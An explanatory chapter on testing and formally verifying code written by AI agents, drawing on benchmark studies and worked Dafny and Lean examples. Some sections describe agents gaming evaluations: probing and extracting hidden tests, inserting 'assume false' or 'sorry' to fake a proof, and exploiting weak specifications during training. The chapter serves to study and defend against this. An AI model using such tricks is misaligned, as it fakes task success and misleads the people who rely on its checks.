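The calculation also assumes that the program was finished before the tests began, but agents usually revise their code until the tests pass. Suppose an agent writes 20 versions of a program, each wrong on 0.3% of inputs, and tests each on 1,000 fresh inputs. Each version has a 5% chance of passing, so the chance that at least one passes is about 64%. If the agent reuses the same inputs, it can fit the program to them, and the bound no longer applies.

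### Comparison with a trusted version

When an agent rewrites a program to make it faster or translate it into another language, the old version's outputs can serve as the expected results. A tester runs both versions on the same inputs, which can include some recorded from real use, and compares the outputs.

The trusted version can also be a separate program that does the same job. Naziri and colleagues describe a test that compared how Python and ArangoDB, a database, replace one piece of text with another. When the text to search was empty, Python returned empty text, but ArangoDB returned no value and a warning. ArangoDB's developers confirmed the bug and fixed it.

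Comparing the old and new versions of a program misses any error they share. The old version also gives the wrong expected results for any behaviour that the user asked to change. Wu, Feng and colleagues (2026), in *Patch correctness in automated program repair*, warn that tests with expected answers copied from a faulty program can preserve the fault that a patch should remove.

A difference between two versions doesn't show which one is wrong, or whether either is. Wang, Pradel and Liu (2025), in *Are "Solved Issues" in SWE-bench Really Solved Correctly?*, studied 877 AI-written patches that had passed the tests in SWE-bench Verified, a set of 500 real problems from Python projects. A language model then wrote more tests to compare each patch with the human programmer's fix, and 29.6% of the patches behaved differently from the fix. The researchers inspected 77 of these patches, judged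 22 wrong and 4 right, and could not decide about the other 51.

### Assertions in production

An assertion is a condition that a program checks while it runs. The conditions in the sorting test could also be assertions inside the sorting function, which would then check every list a user sorts. This removes the problem of unrepresentative test inputs but adds some computation to each run.

Assertions suit agent code because it may run only once, on data that nobody has tested it with. Before each payment, the refund script could check that the payment will not take the total paid above the total owed. If the check came afterwards, a failed assertion would only report the loss. Even with the check before each payment, the script may stop with half the customers paid, and it could still pay the right total to the wrong people.

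This kind of check resembles a policy monitor's, but the agent usually writes the assertion itself and can leave it out or make it too weak. Lahiri reports that assertions written by language models caught one in eight of the real bugs in Defects4J, a collection of faults from large Java projects. They caught some that an older tool had missed.

### Tests that reject right answers

Each SWE-bench problem comes with two kinds of test, which the agent does not see. One kind fails on the original code and passes once the problem is fixed, and the other checks that the rest of the project still works. The tests come from the change a human programmer made to fix the problem, so they may check details of that change that nobody told the agent about.

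In OpenAI's *Why SWE-bench Verified no longer measures frontier coding capabilities* (2026), engineers reviewed 138 problems that the model o3 did not solve consistently in 64 attempts, and found serious flaws in the tests or descriptions of 59.4%. For example, one problem's tests import a function called `get_annotation`, which the problem description doesn't mention, so a correct patch fails if it gives the function another name.

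OpenAI chose problems that the model often failed, so the percentage doesn't apply to the whole benchmark. But it amounts to 82 problems, so at least 16% of the 500 are flawed.

Models sometimes passed such tests because they had seen the answer in training. In one problem, the tests require a parameter called `edit_only`, which the description does not clearly ask for. GPT-5.2's reasoning shows that it had learned the parameter from a later version of the software, so its pass is poor evidence that it could solve a similar new problem.

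OpenAI recommended that developers switch to another benchmark, SWE-Bench Pro, but withdrew the recommendation in July 2026 after a similar audit. OpenAI's *Separating signal from noise in coding evaluations* estimates that about 30% of SWE-Bench Pro's 731 tasks are broken. An automated review supervised by researchers identified 200 broken tasks, and a separate panel of engineers identified 249. Some tests rejected correct programs, while others checked so little of the requested feature that incomplete programs passed. The engineers considered such weak tests the main problem in 9.4% of all tasks, compared with 4.1% in the automated review.

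### Tests that accept wrong answers

One patch that Wang and colleagues studied was for SymPy, a mathematics library. In a certain mode, the library rejected ordinary points because it wrongly concluded that their coordinates were imaginary numbers. The agent's patch turned off the check for imaginary coordinates in that mode. Ordinary points then worked, and the tests passed, but the library also accepted points that it should reject.

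SWE-bench runs only the test files that the human programmer changed. When Wang and colleagues ran all of each project's existing tests, 7.8% of the patches that had passed now failed.

Yu, Cao and colleagues (2026), in *SWE-ABS*, had a model write patches that were deliberately wrong but passed the existing tests, then added tests to catch them. The new tests rejected 19.8% of the patches from leading agents that the old tests had accepted (2,184 of 11,041). The top agent's score fell from 78.8% to 62.2%. In one problem, the code had to convert a database password to text, but the original test used a password that was already text, so it accepted 25 patches that would fail if the password were a number.

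Stronger tests can also be too strict. According to Wu, Feng and colleagues, the *SWE-ABS* team inspected its new tests before the main evaluation and found that those for 53 of the 500 problems depended on details of the human fix. The team revised or removed them. Any overly strict tests it missed would make the share of wrong patches look larger than it is.

Project maintainers judge code on more than whether it passes tests. METR, a research organisation that evaluates AI models, studied this in *Many SWE-bench-passing PRs would not be merged into main* (2026). Four maintainers from three projects reviewed 296 AI-written patches without being told who wrote them. They would have rejected about half of the patches that passed the tests, even after METR adjusted for how strict the maintainers were. METR made this adjustment because the maintainers accepted only 68% of the human-written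 patches in the sample, all of which the projects had already adopted.

Some of the rejected patches failed to fix the problem or broke other code, but others were just badly written. So the study doesn't show that half of the passing patches behave wrongly. The agents also had only one attempt, whereas a human programmer could normally respond to a reviewer's comments. The newest model in the study was Claude Sonnet 4.5, so later models may do better.

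### When an agent games the test

An agent that can access the tests may pass them without doing the task. In June 2026, METR (2026) tried to measure the 50% time horizon of the model GPT-5.6 Sol, which is how long a skilled person would take to do tasks that the model completes half the time. METR detected more cheating than with any other public model it had tested in the same way. In one task, the model hid code in its trial submissions to reveal information about the hidden tests. In another, it extracted hidden source code that gave the expected answer.

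The result depended almost entirely on how METR scored these attempts:

| How METR counts cheating | 50% time horizon | 95% confidence interval |
|---|---|---|
| As failure (METR's standard method) | 11.3 hours | 5 to 40 hours |
| Leave those attempts out | 71 hours | 13 to 11,400 hours |
| As success | Over 270 hours | Not given |

METR does not consider any of these figures robust. The model behaved the same way in all three rows, so the differences come only from the definition of success. If METR had relied on the test results without looking for cheating, it would have reported the largest figure.

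Restricting an agent's file access helps with testing, because the agent cannot copy expected answers from files it cannot read. The testing software also has to run outside the agent's control. Wu, Feng and colleagues describe an early case in which a program that repaired the PHP language's interpreter used the repaired interpreter to help judge its own tests, so a faulty repair could affect whether the tests passed.

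### Agents that write property-based tests

Property-based tests take skill to write, because the tester has to find a rule worth checking and generate inputs that the program should accept. Agents can now do much of this work. In *Agentic Property-Based Testing*, Maaz, DeVoe and colleagues (2025) had an agent running Claude Opus 4.1 read the code and documentation of 100 Python packages, write tests and report the bugs it found. The agent produced 984 reports at an average cost of $5.56 each.

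The researchers reviewed 50 reports, drawn from the 80% that a model had ranked highest, and judged 56% of them valid. One concerned a random-number function in NumPy, a numerical library, that sometimes returned negative numbers because of rounding errors when it never should. NumPy's maintainers accepted a fix. In another case, the agent assumed that a function for computing the date of Easter should always return a Sunday, and tested whether it did. It doesn't for the older Julian calendar, but the maintainers said this was intended.

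Naziri and colleagues tried the same method with Claude Opus 5 on ten larger programs, including the PostgreSQL database and the Clang compiler, and reported 180 bugs. By the time of the study, developers had confirmed 109, rejected 3, and not yet decided on the other 68. Other people had independently reported 44 of the confirmed bugs, which leaves 65 new ones. Only 24 of the 180 were crashes or similar failures. The rest were wrong results, which a tester can detect only by knowing the right result.

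Filtering explains much of the low rejection rate. A model discarded test failures it classified as false alarms, and the researchers read and reproduced each remaining bug before reporting it. In a separate sample of 30 unfiltered test failures, only 9 were real faults. A developer who uses such an agent without a filter can therefore expect most failing tests to be false alarms.

*PBT-Bench* (2026) measures how many bugs the tests miss, using 100 problems with planted bugs in 40 Python libraries. The best agent found 83% of them. No single model was best on the hardest bugs, and all sixteen pairings of model and prompt together found 99.5%. Using several models can therefore catch errors that one would miss, though each additional set of tests may also add false alarms.

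### One model writing both code and tests

These studies tested established software, whose documentation often states what it should do. Documentation supplied the rule for 78% of the tests that Naziri and colleagues examined. A program that an agent has just written may have no documentation except the user's request. If the model misreads the request, its tests can repeat the mistake. In Lahiri's example of removing duplicates, a model that chose the wrong reading would write tests based on that reading, and its program would pass them.

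Wu, Feng and colleagues review an experiment on 449 tasks that measured how far generated tests can be trusted. Two older models wrote patches, and a test-writing tool generated tests. The researchers then took the patches that passed these tests and ran them against the benchmark's own tests, which the agents had not seen.

| Model | Stage | Passed generated tests | Of these, failed hidden tests |
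|---|---|---|---|
| Claude 3.7 Sonnet | First attempt | 229 | 50 (21.8%) |
| Claude 3.7 Sonnet | After revision | 251 | 64 (25.5%) |
| GPT-4o | First attempt | 176 | 58 (33.0%) |
| GPT-4o | After revision | 198 | 71 (35.9%) |

Revising the code with the generated tests raised the number of Claude's patches that passed both sets of tests from 179 to 187, and GPT-4o's from 118 to 127. But passing the generated tests became a less reliable sign that a patch was correct, because the number of wrong patches that passed them rose faster. The experiment doesn't show how many of the errors came from a shared misreading of the task, since weak tests would also let wrong patches pass.

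Newer models write tests that catch most wrong patches but also reject many correct ones. Lu, Wang and colleagues (2026), in *SWEPatchTest*, had models write tests for 619 benchmark tasks, after removing the easiest tasks and those with poor official tests. They ran the models' tests on 82,579 patches that had already passed or failed the official tests.

| Model that wrote the tests | Wrong patches rejected | Right patches accepted |
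|---|---|---|
| GPT-5.6 Sol | 88.57% | 50.20% |
| Claude Opus 5 | 85.91% | 66.76% |
| Claude Opus 4.8 | 74.12% | 76.47% |

GPT-5.6 Sol had the best result of any model, but its tests detected the original fault and classified every patch correctly on only 9.21% of tasks. In one task, its test required an error message when a certain setting was empty, although the task description didn't cover that case. As a result, the test failed a patch that passes the official tests. An agent that revises its code until such a test passes may break a program that was already correct.

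Developers can reduce these problems in several ways, each of which addresses a different cause. If they withhold some tests until the agent has finished, the agent cannot fit its code to them, but this doesn't help if the hidden tests contain the same misreading. Deliberately wrong programs, like those that Yu and colleagues used, reveal tests that are too weak, but a model that has misunderstood the task may also misjudge which programs are wrong. A second model may interpret the request differently, and the disagreement would expose the ambiguity. However, both models may make the same natural mistake.

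An oracle from outside the model is the best protection against a shared misreading. For behaviour that should stay the same, this can be a trusted older version or existing documentation. For new behaviour, the user has to supply the expected answer, for instance by approving or rejecting a few of the proposed tests.

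## Proving that agent code meets a specification

A proof, unlike a test, covers every permitted input. If the user already has a correct specification, the remaining problem is to write a program that meets it and get a verifier to confirm that it does.

### From types that restrict to types that specify

Suppose an agent has to write a function that totals a list of refunds, each a whole number of cents. A plain type requires only that the function take a list of whole numbers and return a whole number, so a function that always returns 0 has this type.

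A refinement type adds a condition on the values, such as "a whole number that is not negative". The function that returns 0 still passes. A dependent type can be stricter because its condition can mention the input, such as "at least as large as every refund in the list". This excludes the function that returns 0 but allows one that counts every refund twice. Only the full postcondition, that the result equals the sum of the list, leaves a single correct answer.

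| Required result | Always returns 0 | Counts each refund twice | Adds each refund once |
|---|---|---|---|
| A whole number | Accepted | Accepted | Accepted |
| Not negative | Accepted | Accepted | Accepted |
| At least as large as every refund | Rejected | Accepted | Accepted |
| Equal to the sum | Rejected | Rejected | Accepted |

In Lean, a language for writing programs and proofs, the last row can itself be a type:

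```
def total (xs : List Nat) : { t : Nat // t = xs.sum }
```

The part in braces describes the numbers `t` that equal the sum of `xs`. To return a value of this type, a program must supply the number and a proof that it equals the sum. The function that returns 0 cannot supply this proof, because the list might contain a refund of 4,000 cents.

Parametric types exclude errors in a different way. If a function takes a list of *A* and returns a list of *A*, and must work for every type *A*, its code cannot create or examine an *A*, so every item in the result must come from the input. Such a function could reorder, drop or repeat refunds, but it could not invent one or change an amount. This property, called parametricity, holds for every program of that type, much like a restriction guarantee. It fails in languages where code can inspect or cast a value of unknown type.

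Even plain types can specify a little, as when separate types for old and new contracts rule out the swapped comparison.

### How much plain types help a model

A language model writes a program one token at a time. In type-constrained generation, software checks each token before adding it. *Type-Constrained Code Generation with Language Models* (Mündler, He and colleagues, 2025) describes such a checker for part of TypeScript, a widely used typed language. The checker rejects a token if adding it would leave no way to complete the program with correct types, and the software then picks another from the model's suggestions.

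In one example, the unfinished program ends with `parseInt(num`. The variable `num` is a number, but `parseInt` requires text. The checker rejects `, 10)`, which would pass the number unchanged, and accepts `.toString()`, which converts it to text.

The researchers tested six open models on two sets of short programming problems, HumanEval and MBPP. The checker reduced compilation failures by 74.8% on HumanEval and 56.0% on MBPP. The share of correct programs rose by an average of only 3.5% relative to its previous value. For example, Qwen2.5 32B improved from 79.6% to 81.8% on HumanEval. Most wrong programs already had correct types. By the paper's figures, only 17 of Qwen2.5 32B's roughly 130 wrong programs on HumanEval failed to compile.

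In *The Alignment Problem in Constrained Code Generation*, Biagiola, Cesario and colleagues (2026) later ran the same checker on the same six models and found that, in nearly every comparison, the models wrote correct programs more often without it. Qwen2.5 32B solved 82.3% of HumanEval problems without the checker and 72.3% with it. The checker supports only part of TypeScript, so it blocks some valid programs. In one case it blocked a call to `isPalindrome`, a function the model would have defined later in the program. The model called the built-in `isNaN` instead, and the program compiled but gave wrong answers.

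The two results are compatible. Mündler and colleagues used the checker only to redo programs that had failed to compile, so it could not break a program that was already valid. Both studies used models from 2024 or earlier. Stronger models probably make fewer type errors on such short problems, leaving even fewer for plain types to correct.

### Proving the totalling loop

The following version of the function is in Dafny, a programming language with a built-in verifier:

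```
function Sum(xs: seq<nat>, n: nat): nat
  requires n <= |xs|
{ if n == 0 then 0 else Sum(xs, n - 1) + xs[n - 1] }

method Total(xs: seq<nat>) returns (t: nat)
  ensures t == Sum(xs, |xs|)
{
  t := 0;
  var i := 0;
  while i < |xs|
    invariant 0 <= i <= |xs|
    invariant t == Sum(xs, i)
  {
    t := t + xs[i];
    i := i + 1;
  }
}
```

`Sum(xs, n)` defines the sum of the first `n` refunds, and `|xs|` is the length of the list. The `ensures` line is the postcondition.

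The verifier cannot simply run the loop, because the list may have any length. It relies on loop invariants, which are statements that hold before the loop starts and after every pass. The first invariant keeps `i` within the list. The second is that `t` equals the sum of the first `i` refunds. From the code and the invariants, Dafny generates conditions that together imply the postcondition. The main ones are:

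1. **Start.** With `t` and `i` both 0, *0 = Sum(xs, 0)*.
2. **Each pass.** If *t = Sum(xs, i)* and *0 ≤ i < |xs|*, then *t + xs[i] = Sum(xs, i + 1)*.
3. **End.** If *t = Sum(xs, i)*, *i ≤ |xs|* and the loop has stopped, then *t = Sum(xs, |xs|)*.
4. **Safety.** Whenever the program reads `xs[i]`, the list has an item at that position.
5. **Termination.** The number of refunds left, *|xs| − i*, shrinks on every pass and never falls below 0.

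Without the termination condition, the proof would show only partial correctness, which an infinite loop satisfies.

Dafny passes the conditions to an SMT solver, a program that looks for values that make a set of formulas true together. To prove the second condition, the solver assumes that it fails for some list:

*0 ≤ i < |xs|, t = Sum(xs, i) and t + xs[i] ≠ Sum(xs, i + 1).*

By definition, *Sum(xs, i + 1) = Sum(xs, i) + xs[i]*. Replacing *Sum(xs, i)* with *t* turns the last formula into *t + xs[i] ≠ t + xs[i]*, which is impossible. No counterexample exists, so the condition holds for lists of every length. For the third condition, the loop stops only when *i ≥ |xs|*, and *i* is never more than *|xs|*, so the two are equal.

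Suppose the agent writes `while i < |xs| - 1`, which leaves out the last refund. The loop can then stop when *i = |xs| − 1*, so the third condition fails and Dafny rejects the program.

Dafny also rejects the correct program if the agent omits the second invariant, because nothing then connects `t` with the refunds. So a rejection can mean that the program is wrong or only that the proof is incomplete.

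### Automatic verifiers and proof assistants

Dafny is an automatic verifier, and so is Verus, which checks programs written in the language Rust. The programmer writes the specification and annotations such as invariants, and the solver finds the routine steps. In a proof assistant such as Lean, the programmer usually writes the proof as a series of commands called tactics. A Lean version of the totalling function and its proof could look like this:

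```
def total : List Nat → Nat
  | [] => 0
  | x :: rest => x + total rest

theorem total_correct (xs : List Nat) : total xs = xs.sum := by
  induction xs with
  | nil => simp [total]
  | cons x rest ih => simp [total, ih]
```

The function adds the first refund to the total of the rest. The proof first shows that the claim holds for the empty list. It then shows that if the claim holds for a list (the assumption `ih`), it also holds for that list with one more refund at the front. This induction serves the same purpose as the loop invariant in Dafny.

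Tan (2026) notes in *Automating Formal Verification with Reinforcement Learning and Recursive Inference* that more automation makes proofs faster to write but limits what they can express, while a proof assistant allows a wider range of mathematical reasoning but takes more work. An SMT solver can also run out of time on a true condition, and the programmer then has to work out which extra fact would help it.

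### The vericoding benchmark

*A Benchmark for Vericoding* (Bursuc, Ehrenborg and colleagues, 2025) defines "vericoding" as generating verified code from a formal specification. The benchmark, released in September 2025, has 12,504 specifications: 3,029 in Dafny, 2,334 in Verus and 7,141 in Lean. One task is to write a function that adds two binary numbers stored as lists of digits. Its specification requires the result to be a valid binary number equal to the sum of the inputs.

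The model has to write both the code and the proof. If the verifier rejects them, the model receives the error messages and tries again. It gets five attempts on most tasks. The researchers tested nine models on the tasks that passed their quality checks.

| Language | Solved by at least one model | Best single model |
|---|---|---|
| Dafny | 82% | 67.5% (Claude Opus 4.1) |
| Verus | 44% | 30.9% (GPT-5) |
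| Lean | 27% | 17.9% (GPT-5) |

The widely quoted success rates are those in the middle column, so they overstate what a user could expect from any one model.

Bursuc and colleagues suggest several reasons for the differences between languages. Dafny's whole numbers have no upper limit, but Rust's do, so a Verus proof must also show that no calculation exceeds the limit. For instance, a total stored as a 32-bit number of cents would overflow at about $21 million. For Lean, they suggest that models had trained mostly on mathematical proofs rather than proofs about programs. Their setup also showed the model the state of its proof only five times per task, whereas a person writing Lean sees it constantly.

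*AlgoVeri* (2026), another benchmark, makes the comparison stricter by setting the same 77 classical algorithms in all three languages. It reports that Gemini-3 Flash solved 40.3% of them in Dafny, and attributes this success to Dafny's high-level features and its solver.

Bursuc and colleagues found that the models wrote code easily but had more trouble with proofs. Models were already getting better at writing proofs for code they were given. On DafnyBench, a set of 782 human-written Dafny programs whose annotations the model must restore, the best result rose from 68% in June 2024 to 89% with Claude Opus 4.1.

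### Newer models and better search

How much models have improved since then depends on how they are tested. *Automating Formal Verification with Agent-Guided Tree Search* (2026) reran 423 of the benchmark's Lean tasks on newer models with their step-by-step reasoning turned off. GPT-5.4 scored highest, at 24.6%, and the closed American models gained at most four percentage points over their predecessors.

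Agents that can reason and use the proof tools do much better than models limited to one attempt. The creators of VeriContest, a benchmark of 1,007 competitive-programming problems in Rust, reported that the best model, given the specification and the code, produced a valid Verus proof on the first attempt for only 13.95% of the problems. Serbanuta, Xu and colleagues (2026), in *Solving VeriContest with a Lean-Backed Rust Verifier*, translated the problems into Lean and let agents work on the proofs. Every current frontier model proved nearly all of a small sample of ten theorems, even at low reasoning effort. The agents were not limited to one attempt, so the improvement does not come from Lean alone.

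Tan likewise improved results without changing the model. His software divides a Lean proof into smaller goals, returns the error messages and repairs failed steps. This raised the success rate on a pilot set from 46.2% to 69.2%.

### Training a model with a verifier

In reinforcement learning, a model makes many attempts and training strengthens whatever received a high reward. A verifier can supply the reward automatically. But if it only reports success or failure, failed attempts in a group all get the same score, and when every attempt fails, the model learns nothing from the one that came closest.

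*Verifier-Grounded Agentic RL for Provably Correct Code* (Ma, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) therefore rewards the share of proof obligations, such as the five conditions above, that an attempt satisfies. It fixes the list of obligations before the attempt starts so that a model can't earn credit by adding and proving trivial invariants such as `true`.

A 35-billion-parameter version of Qwen3.6 was trained on DafnyBench programs and tested on held-out programs. In one task the model only restored missing annotations, while in the other it wrote both the code and the proof.

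| Training | Annotations only | Code and proof |
|---|---|---|
| None | 67.4% | 66.1% |
| Imitating finished proofs | 60.9% | 53.2% |
| Reward for complete success only | 75.2% | 71.0% |
| Reward for each obligation | 76.7% | 93.5% |

In the last two rows, a second model helped the first finish its proofs when the first wrote both code and proof. Without this help, the best result fell from 93.5% to 88.7%. The researchers chose the version of the model that did best on the held-out programs, so all the trained models' scores are probably a little high.

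Claude Opus 4.7, which did not receive this training, reached 95.4% on annotations and 97.6% on code and proof. The trained model nearly matched this much stronger model when it wrote its own code, but not when it had to prove someone else's code correct. The trained model may have written code that was easier to prove.

The skills partly carried over to Verus, a language the model had not trained on, where its success rate on short programs rose from 17.2% to 36.6%.

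A model's reward can rise without the model getting better at the intended tasks. In Tan's first Dafny experiment, the reward rose from 2.2% to 58.1%, but the model had learned to exploit weak specifications. After he removed the vulnerable tasks and let the model revise its attempts, training raised the success rate from 9.7% to 31.1%.

### Verified programs of realistic size

Most of these tasks require only one function. In a larger program, the proof for one function depends on facts about others, and changing a function can invalidate proofs elsewhere. *Vero* (Ye, Lou and colleagues, 2026) tested agents on 43 Lean projects based on existing software, including blockchain protocols, distributed systems and popular Python libraries. The projects have 743 functions to write and 2,705 specifications to prove.

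One example in the paper is a bank ledger. One specification requires that, for every ledger and every account number not yet in use, creating the account gives it a balance of zero. The agent has to write the functions for creating accounts and reading balances, then prove that they meet this and the other specifications.

With 90 minutes per project, GPT-5.5 at its highest reasoning setting completed 27 of the 43 projects. Claude Opus 4.8 completed 8, though it was often still writing proofs when time ran out. There were ten projects that no agent completed, even when the researchers supplied working code and asked only for proofs. Newer models may do better.

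GPT-5.5 proved 87.3% of the individual specifications, but most of the 16 projects it did not complete were far from finished. Nine had more than ten specifications left to prove, and only six had five or fewer. The user can't tell from a missing proof alone whether the code is wrong. The unproved specifications often depended on the same few unproved facts. Agents that completed a project usually proved such shared facts once and reused them.

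The proofs were far longer than the code. GPT-5.5's median project had 65 lines of code and 1,077 lines of proof, or about 17 lines of proof per line of code. Tan gives a range of 3 to 10 lines of proof per line of code for published verification projects, many of which took experts years.

In five cases, agents replaced an efficient algorithm with a simpler one that was easier to prove correct. The new code was less efficient but still met every specification, because none of them covered efficiency.

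### Assumptions that the agent adds

Verifiers usually let programmers assume a fact without proving it, which is useful while a proof is unfinished. An agent could use this to replace the body of the totalling function with:

```
{
  assume false;
  t := 0;
}
```

The verifier now only has to prove that *if false is true, then 0 = Sum(xs, |xs|)*. An implication with a false premise is always true, so the condition holds even though the function returns 0 for every list. In Lean, `sorry` can stand in for any missing proof, and a false axiom makes every statement provable.

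An agent under pressure to satisfy a verifier has a reason to use such shortcuts. In the experiment by Ye and colleagues, the checks rejected 14% of GPT-5.5's unfinished specifications as cheating. A system that accepts proofs from an agent must therefore reject any assumption the agent adds. It must also compare the specification with the original, because the agent could replace the postcondition with `ensures true`.

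Ye and colleagues copy only the agent's permitted edits into a fresh version of the project, then reject any proof that depends on an axiom outside an approved list. They also look for uses of a Lean feature that lets the computer run a different function from the one in the proof, since even a valid proof may then not apply to the running program.

Ma and colleagues build such checks into the reward. Leaving out small deductions for wasted turns, the score of an attempt is:

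*score = Ω − A − 3P + 2V*

Here Ω is the weighted share of obligations proved, between 0 and 1. *A* is 1 if the agent changed the specification, *P* is 1 if it assumed something it should have proved, and *V* is 1 if the whole program verifies and passes both checks. Each is otherwise 0. An honest partial proof scores between 0 and 1, and a complete one scores at least 2. An attempt with a forbidden assumption scores −2 or less, below the −1.5 for submitting nothing. The agent therefore gains nothing from cheating that the checks detect.

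### What a proof leaves in the trusted base

Even a proof written in good faith depends on the software that checks it. Users of Dafny or Verus have to trust the part of the tool that generates the logical conditions to be proved, and normally the SMT solver that checks them. A fault in either could make the verifier accept a wrong program. Lean checks every completed proof with a comparatively small program called the kernel, so a fault in a tactic or in the model that wrote the proof cannot by itself make an invalid proof pass.

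The compiler is also in the trusted base, unless somebody has verified it. The proof is about the source code, and a compiler error could make the running program behave differently. The libraries, operating system and hardware must also work as assumed.

Sometimes the proof is about a translation or simplified model of the program, and tests provide the evidence that it applies to the code people run. Serbanuta and colleagues prove theorems about Lean translations of Rust programs, so their result depends on the translation being accurate. They ran both versions on 19,555 test cases and got the same output every time. Amazon Web Services also combines proof with testing for Cedar, its language for access rules. According to Tan, the company wrote a Lean specification of Cedar and rigorously tests it against the Rust program that customers use.

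The link between the program that is verified and the code that is used can be weak. In another experiment by Ma and colleagues, an agent had to repair a Python project and also write a separate program that captured the required behaviour and could be verified. With a second model helping on the proofs, 88.1% of the separate programs passed verification after training, but only 72.5% of the repairs passed the project's own tests. The proof covered only the separate program, so the repair could still be wrong.

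A proof about agent code also has to rely on a contract for each tool the code calls, because the verifier cannot examine the tools themselves. Suppose a refund script calls a payment tool whose contract specifies that each call pays the customer once. The verifier can then prove that the script pays every customer exactly what she is owed. If the tool loses its connection and sends a payment again, the customer is paid twice, even though the proof contains no mistake. The shop would need to compare the bank's records with the amounts owed to find the error.

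## Whether the specification says what the user meant

A proof doesn't show whether the specification says what the user meant, so that needs a separate check.

### The intent gap

Lahiri calls the distance between what a user means and what a program does the intent gap. In his example, a request to remove duplicates from [1, 2, 3, 2, 4] could reasonably mean [1, 2, 3, 4] or [1, 3, 4]. A model will typically write one line of Python that keeps one copy of each number. If the user wanted every repeated number gone, that program is wrong, but it looks reasonable and gives the expected answer for any list without repeats, so a quick trial may not reveal the problem.

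A postcondition can separate the two readings. Lahiri expresses the one that leads to [1, 3, 4] as two assertions:

- Every number in the result occurs exactly once in the input.
- Every number that occurs exactly once in the input is in the result.

The assertions reject [1, 2, 3, 4] because 2 occurs twice in the input. But they accept [1, 1, 3, 4] because they don't limit how often a number may appear in the result. A program could therefore meet this specification for removing duplicates and still return a list that contains a duplicate. The assertions also accept [4, 3, 1], and only the user knows whether the order matters.

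### Soundness and completeness

A specification can be too strict or too loose. In Lahiri's terms, a sound specification doesn't reject correct behaviour, and a complete one rejects incorrect behaviour. Both can be measured against a set of tests *T*, where each test pairs an input *i* with a correct output *o*:

- A specification *S* is sound on *T* if it accepts every pair (*i*, *o*) in *T*.
- The completeness of *S* on *T* is the share of altered pairs (*i*, *o*′) that it rejects, where *o*′ is a wrong output made by changing *o*.

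A specification that accepts everything is perfectly sound but has a completeness of zero, and one that rejects everything is fully complete but unsound. A developer can use both measures before anyone writes the code, because neither requires a program.

Lahiri applies the measures to a Dafny specification that GPT-4 wrote for a function returning the common elements of two arrays, `a` and `b`. Expert reviewers had labelled it "strong". One clause forbids repeats in the result, and the other is:

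```
ensures forall x :: x in result ==> (InArray(a, x) && InArray(b, x))
```

The arrow `==>` means "implies". Everything in the result must be in both arrays, but an element in both arrays doesn't have to be in the result. Replacing the arrow with `<==>` makes the condition work in both directions. If `a` is [1, 2, 3] and `b` is [2, 3, 4], the two versions treat possible outputs as follows:

| Output | With `==>` | With `<==>` |
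|---|---|---|
| [2, 3] (correct) | Accepted | Accepted |
| [] | Accepted | Rejected |
| [2] | Accepted | Rejected |
| [2, 3, 4] | Rejected | Rejected |
| [2, 2, 3] | Rejected | Rejected |

The one-way version accepts the empty list because an empty list has no elements that could break the rule. A function that always returned an empty list would therefore pass the verifier.

Both versions are sound on this test. On these four wrong outputs, the one-way version scores 50% for completeness and the two-way version scores 100%. The score depends on which wrong outputs the tester tries. With only the last two, both versions would score 100%. Lahiri therefore wants the wrong outputs to resemble mistakes that people and AI models make.

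Tests of this kind catch errors that experts miss. *VeriContest* (Xie, Pawagi and colleagues, 2026) is a benchmark whose current version has 1,006 programming problems with specifications. After experts had reviewed the specifications, the researchers turned most of the postconditions into small programs and ran them on wrong outputs. They found 60 postconditions that accepted a wrong answer. One was for a function that finds the first and last positions of a number in a sorted list. It accepted −9 and −8, which are not valid positions.

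If a model bases the tests on a misreading of the request, a specification that matches what the user meant will count as unsound. Tests are still useful because a user can judge an example more easily than a formula.

### Asking the user about examples

TiCoder, a system described by Fakhoury, Naik and colleagues (2024), in *LLM-based Test-driven Interactive Code Generation*, looks for the examples most worth showing to the user. It works in four steps:

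1. A model reads the request and writes several candidate programs and several tests.
2. TiCoder runs every test on every candidate.
3. It shows the user the test that divides the candidates most evenly, and asks whether the expected output is right.
4. It discards the candidates that conflict with her answer, then either asks about another test or shows her the remaining programs.

If *p* candidates pass a test and *f* fail it, the test's score is:

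*score = min(p, f) / max(p, f)*

Suppose a model writes ten programs for removing duplicates. Six keep one copy of each number, and four drop every repeated number. A test that expects [1, 2, 3, 4] from [1, 2, 3, 2, 4] scores 4/6, or about 0.67, because four programs fail it and six pass. A test that expects [1, 2, 3] from [1, 2, 3] scores 0, because all ten programs pass it. TiCoder asks the user about the higher-scoring test, and if the user rejects it, TiCoder discards the six programs that keep one copy.

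If all ten programs kept one copy, no test would distinguish them on this point, and TiCoder would not ask about it. The method detects an ambiguity only if each reading appears in some of the programs the model generates. Lahiri adds that generating enough different candidates becomes expensive for large pieces of code.

### The study of 15 programmers

Fakhoury and colleagues tested TiCoder with 15 programmers. Each programmer did three tasks, each with a different assistant. In each task, the programmer had to decide which of five AI-written suggestions for a short Python function, if any, was correct. One assistant showed all five at once. The other two first asked the programmer about two tests, then removed the suggestions that conflicted with the answers.

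| Assistant | Correct decisions | Average time | Reported mental load (0–100) |
|---|---|---|---|
| Shows all suggestions | 40% | 328 seconds | 45.5 |
| Asks whether each test is right | 84% | 284 seconds | 28.0 |
| Asks for each test's expected output | 64% | 254 seconds | 29.5 |

The rise from 40% to 84% was statistically significant, but the rise to 64% was not. Both versions of TiCoder significantly reduced mental load, but the differences in time could be due to chance.

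The study was small, with 15 participants. Lahiri describes them as professional developers, but the study's table lists nine as academics. The researchers chose tests that would remove one or two wrong suggestions if the programmer answered correctly, so programmers who used TiCoder usually had three or four suggestions to compare instead of five. TiCoder is meant to help partly by narrowing the choice, but in ordinary use its questions may remove fewer suggestions.

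Approving an answer was easier than supplying one. One task was to find the smallest number, counting from 0, that was missing from a sorted list. For the list [1, 2, 4, 6], the answer is 0. Everyone who was shown this answer approved it, but half of those who had to supply their own wrote 3. Fakhoury and colleagues warn that if TiCoder had proposed 3, some people might have approved that too.

If a user answers a question wrongly, TiCoder discards every correct program, so the researchers consider it essential that users can skip questions. Their larger experiment does not measure the effect of wrong answers, because it replaced the user with software that knew the correct program. With up to five questions per problem, the share of problems for which the model's top program was correct rose by about 46 percentage points on average. The first paper on the system, *Interactive Code Generation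 via Test-Driven User-Intent Formalization* (2022), also used simulated users.

### Proofs that establish very little

When a model writes the specification and nobody checks it, a successful proof may be only weak evidence that the program does what the user meant. Vempaty, Sompalle and colleagues (2026), in *Verified but Vacuous*, reproduced an earlier system in which a model writes a program in Dafny, the verifier checks it, and other software translates it into Python. They ran it with Claude Opus 4.7 ten times on each of the 164 HumanEval problems. The verifier accepted 1,625 of 1,640 programs, or 99.1%.

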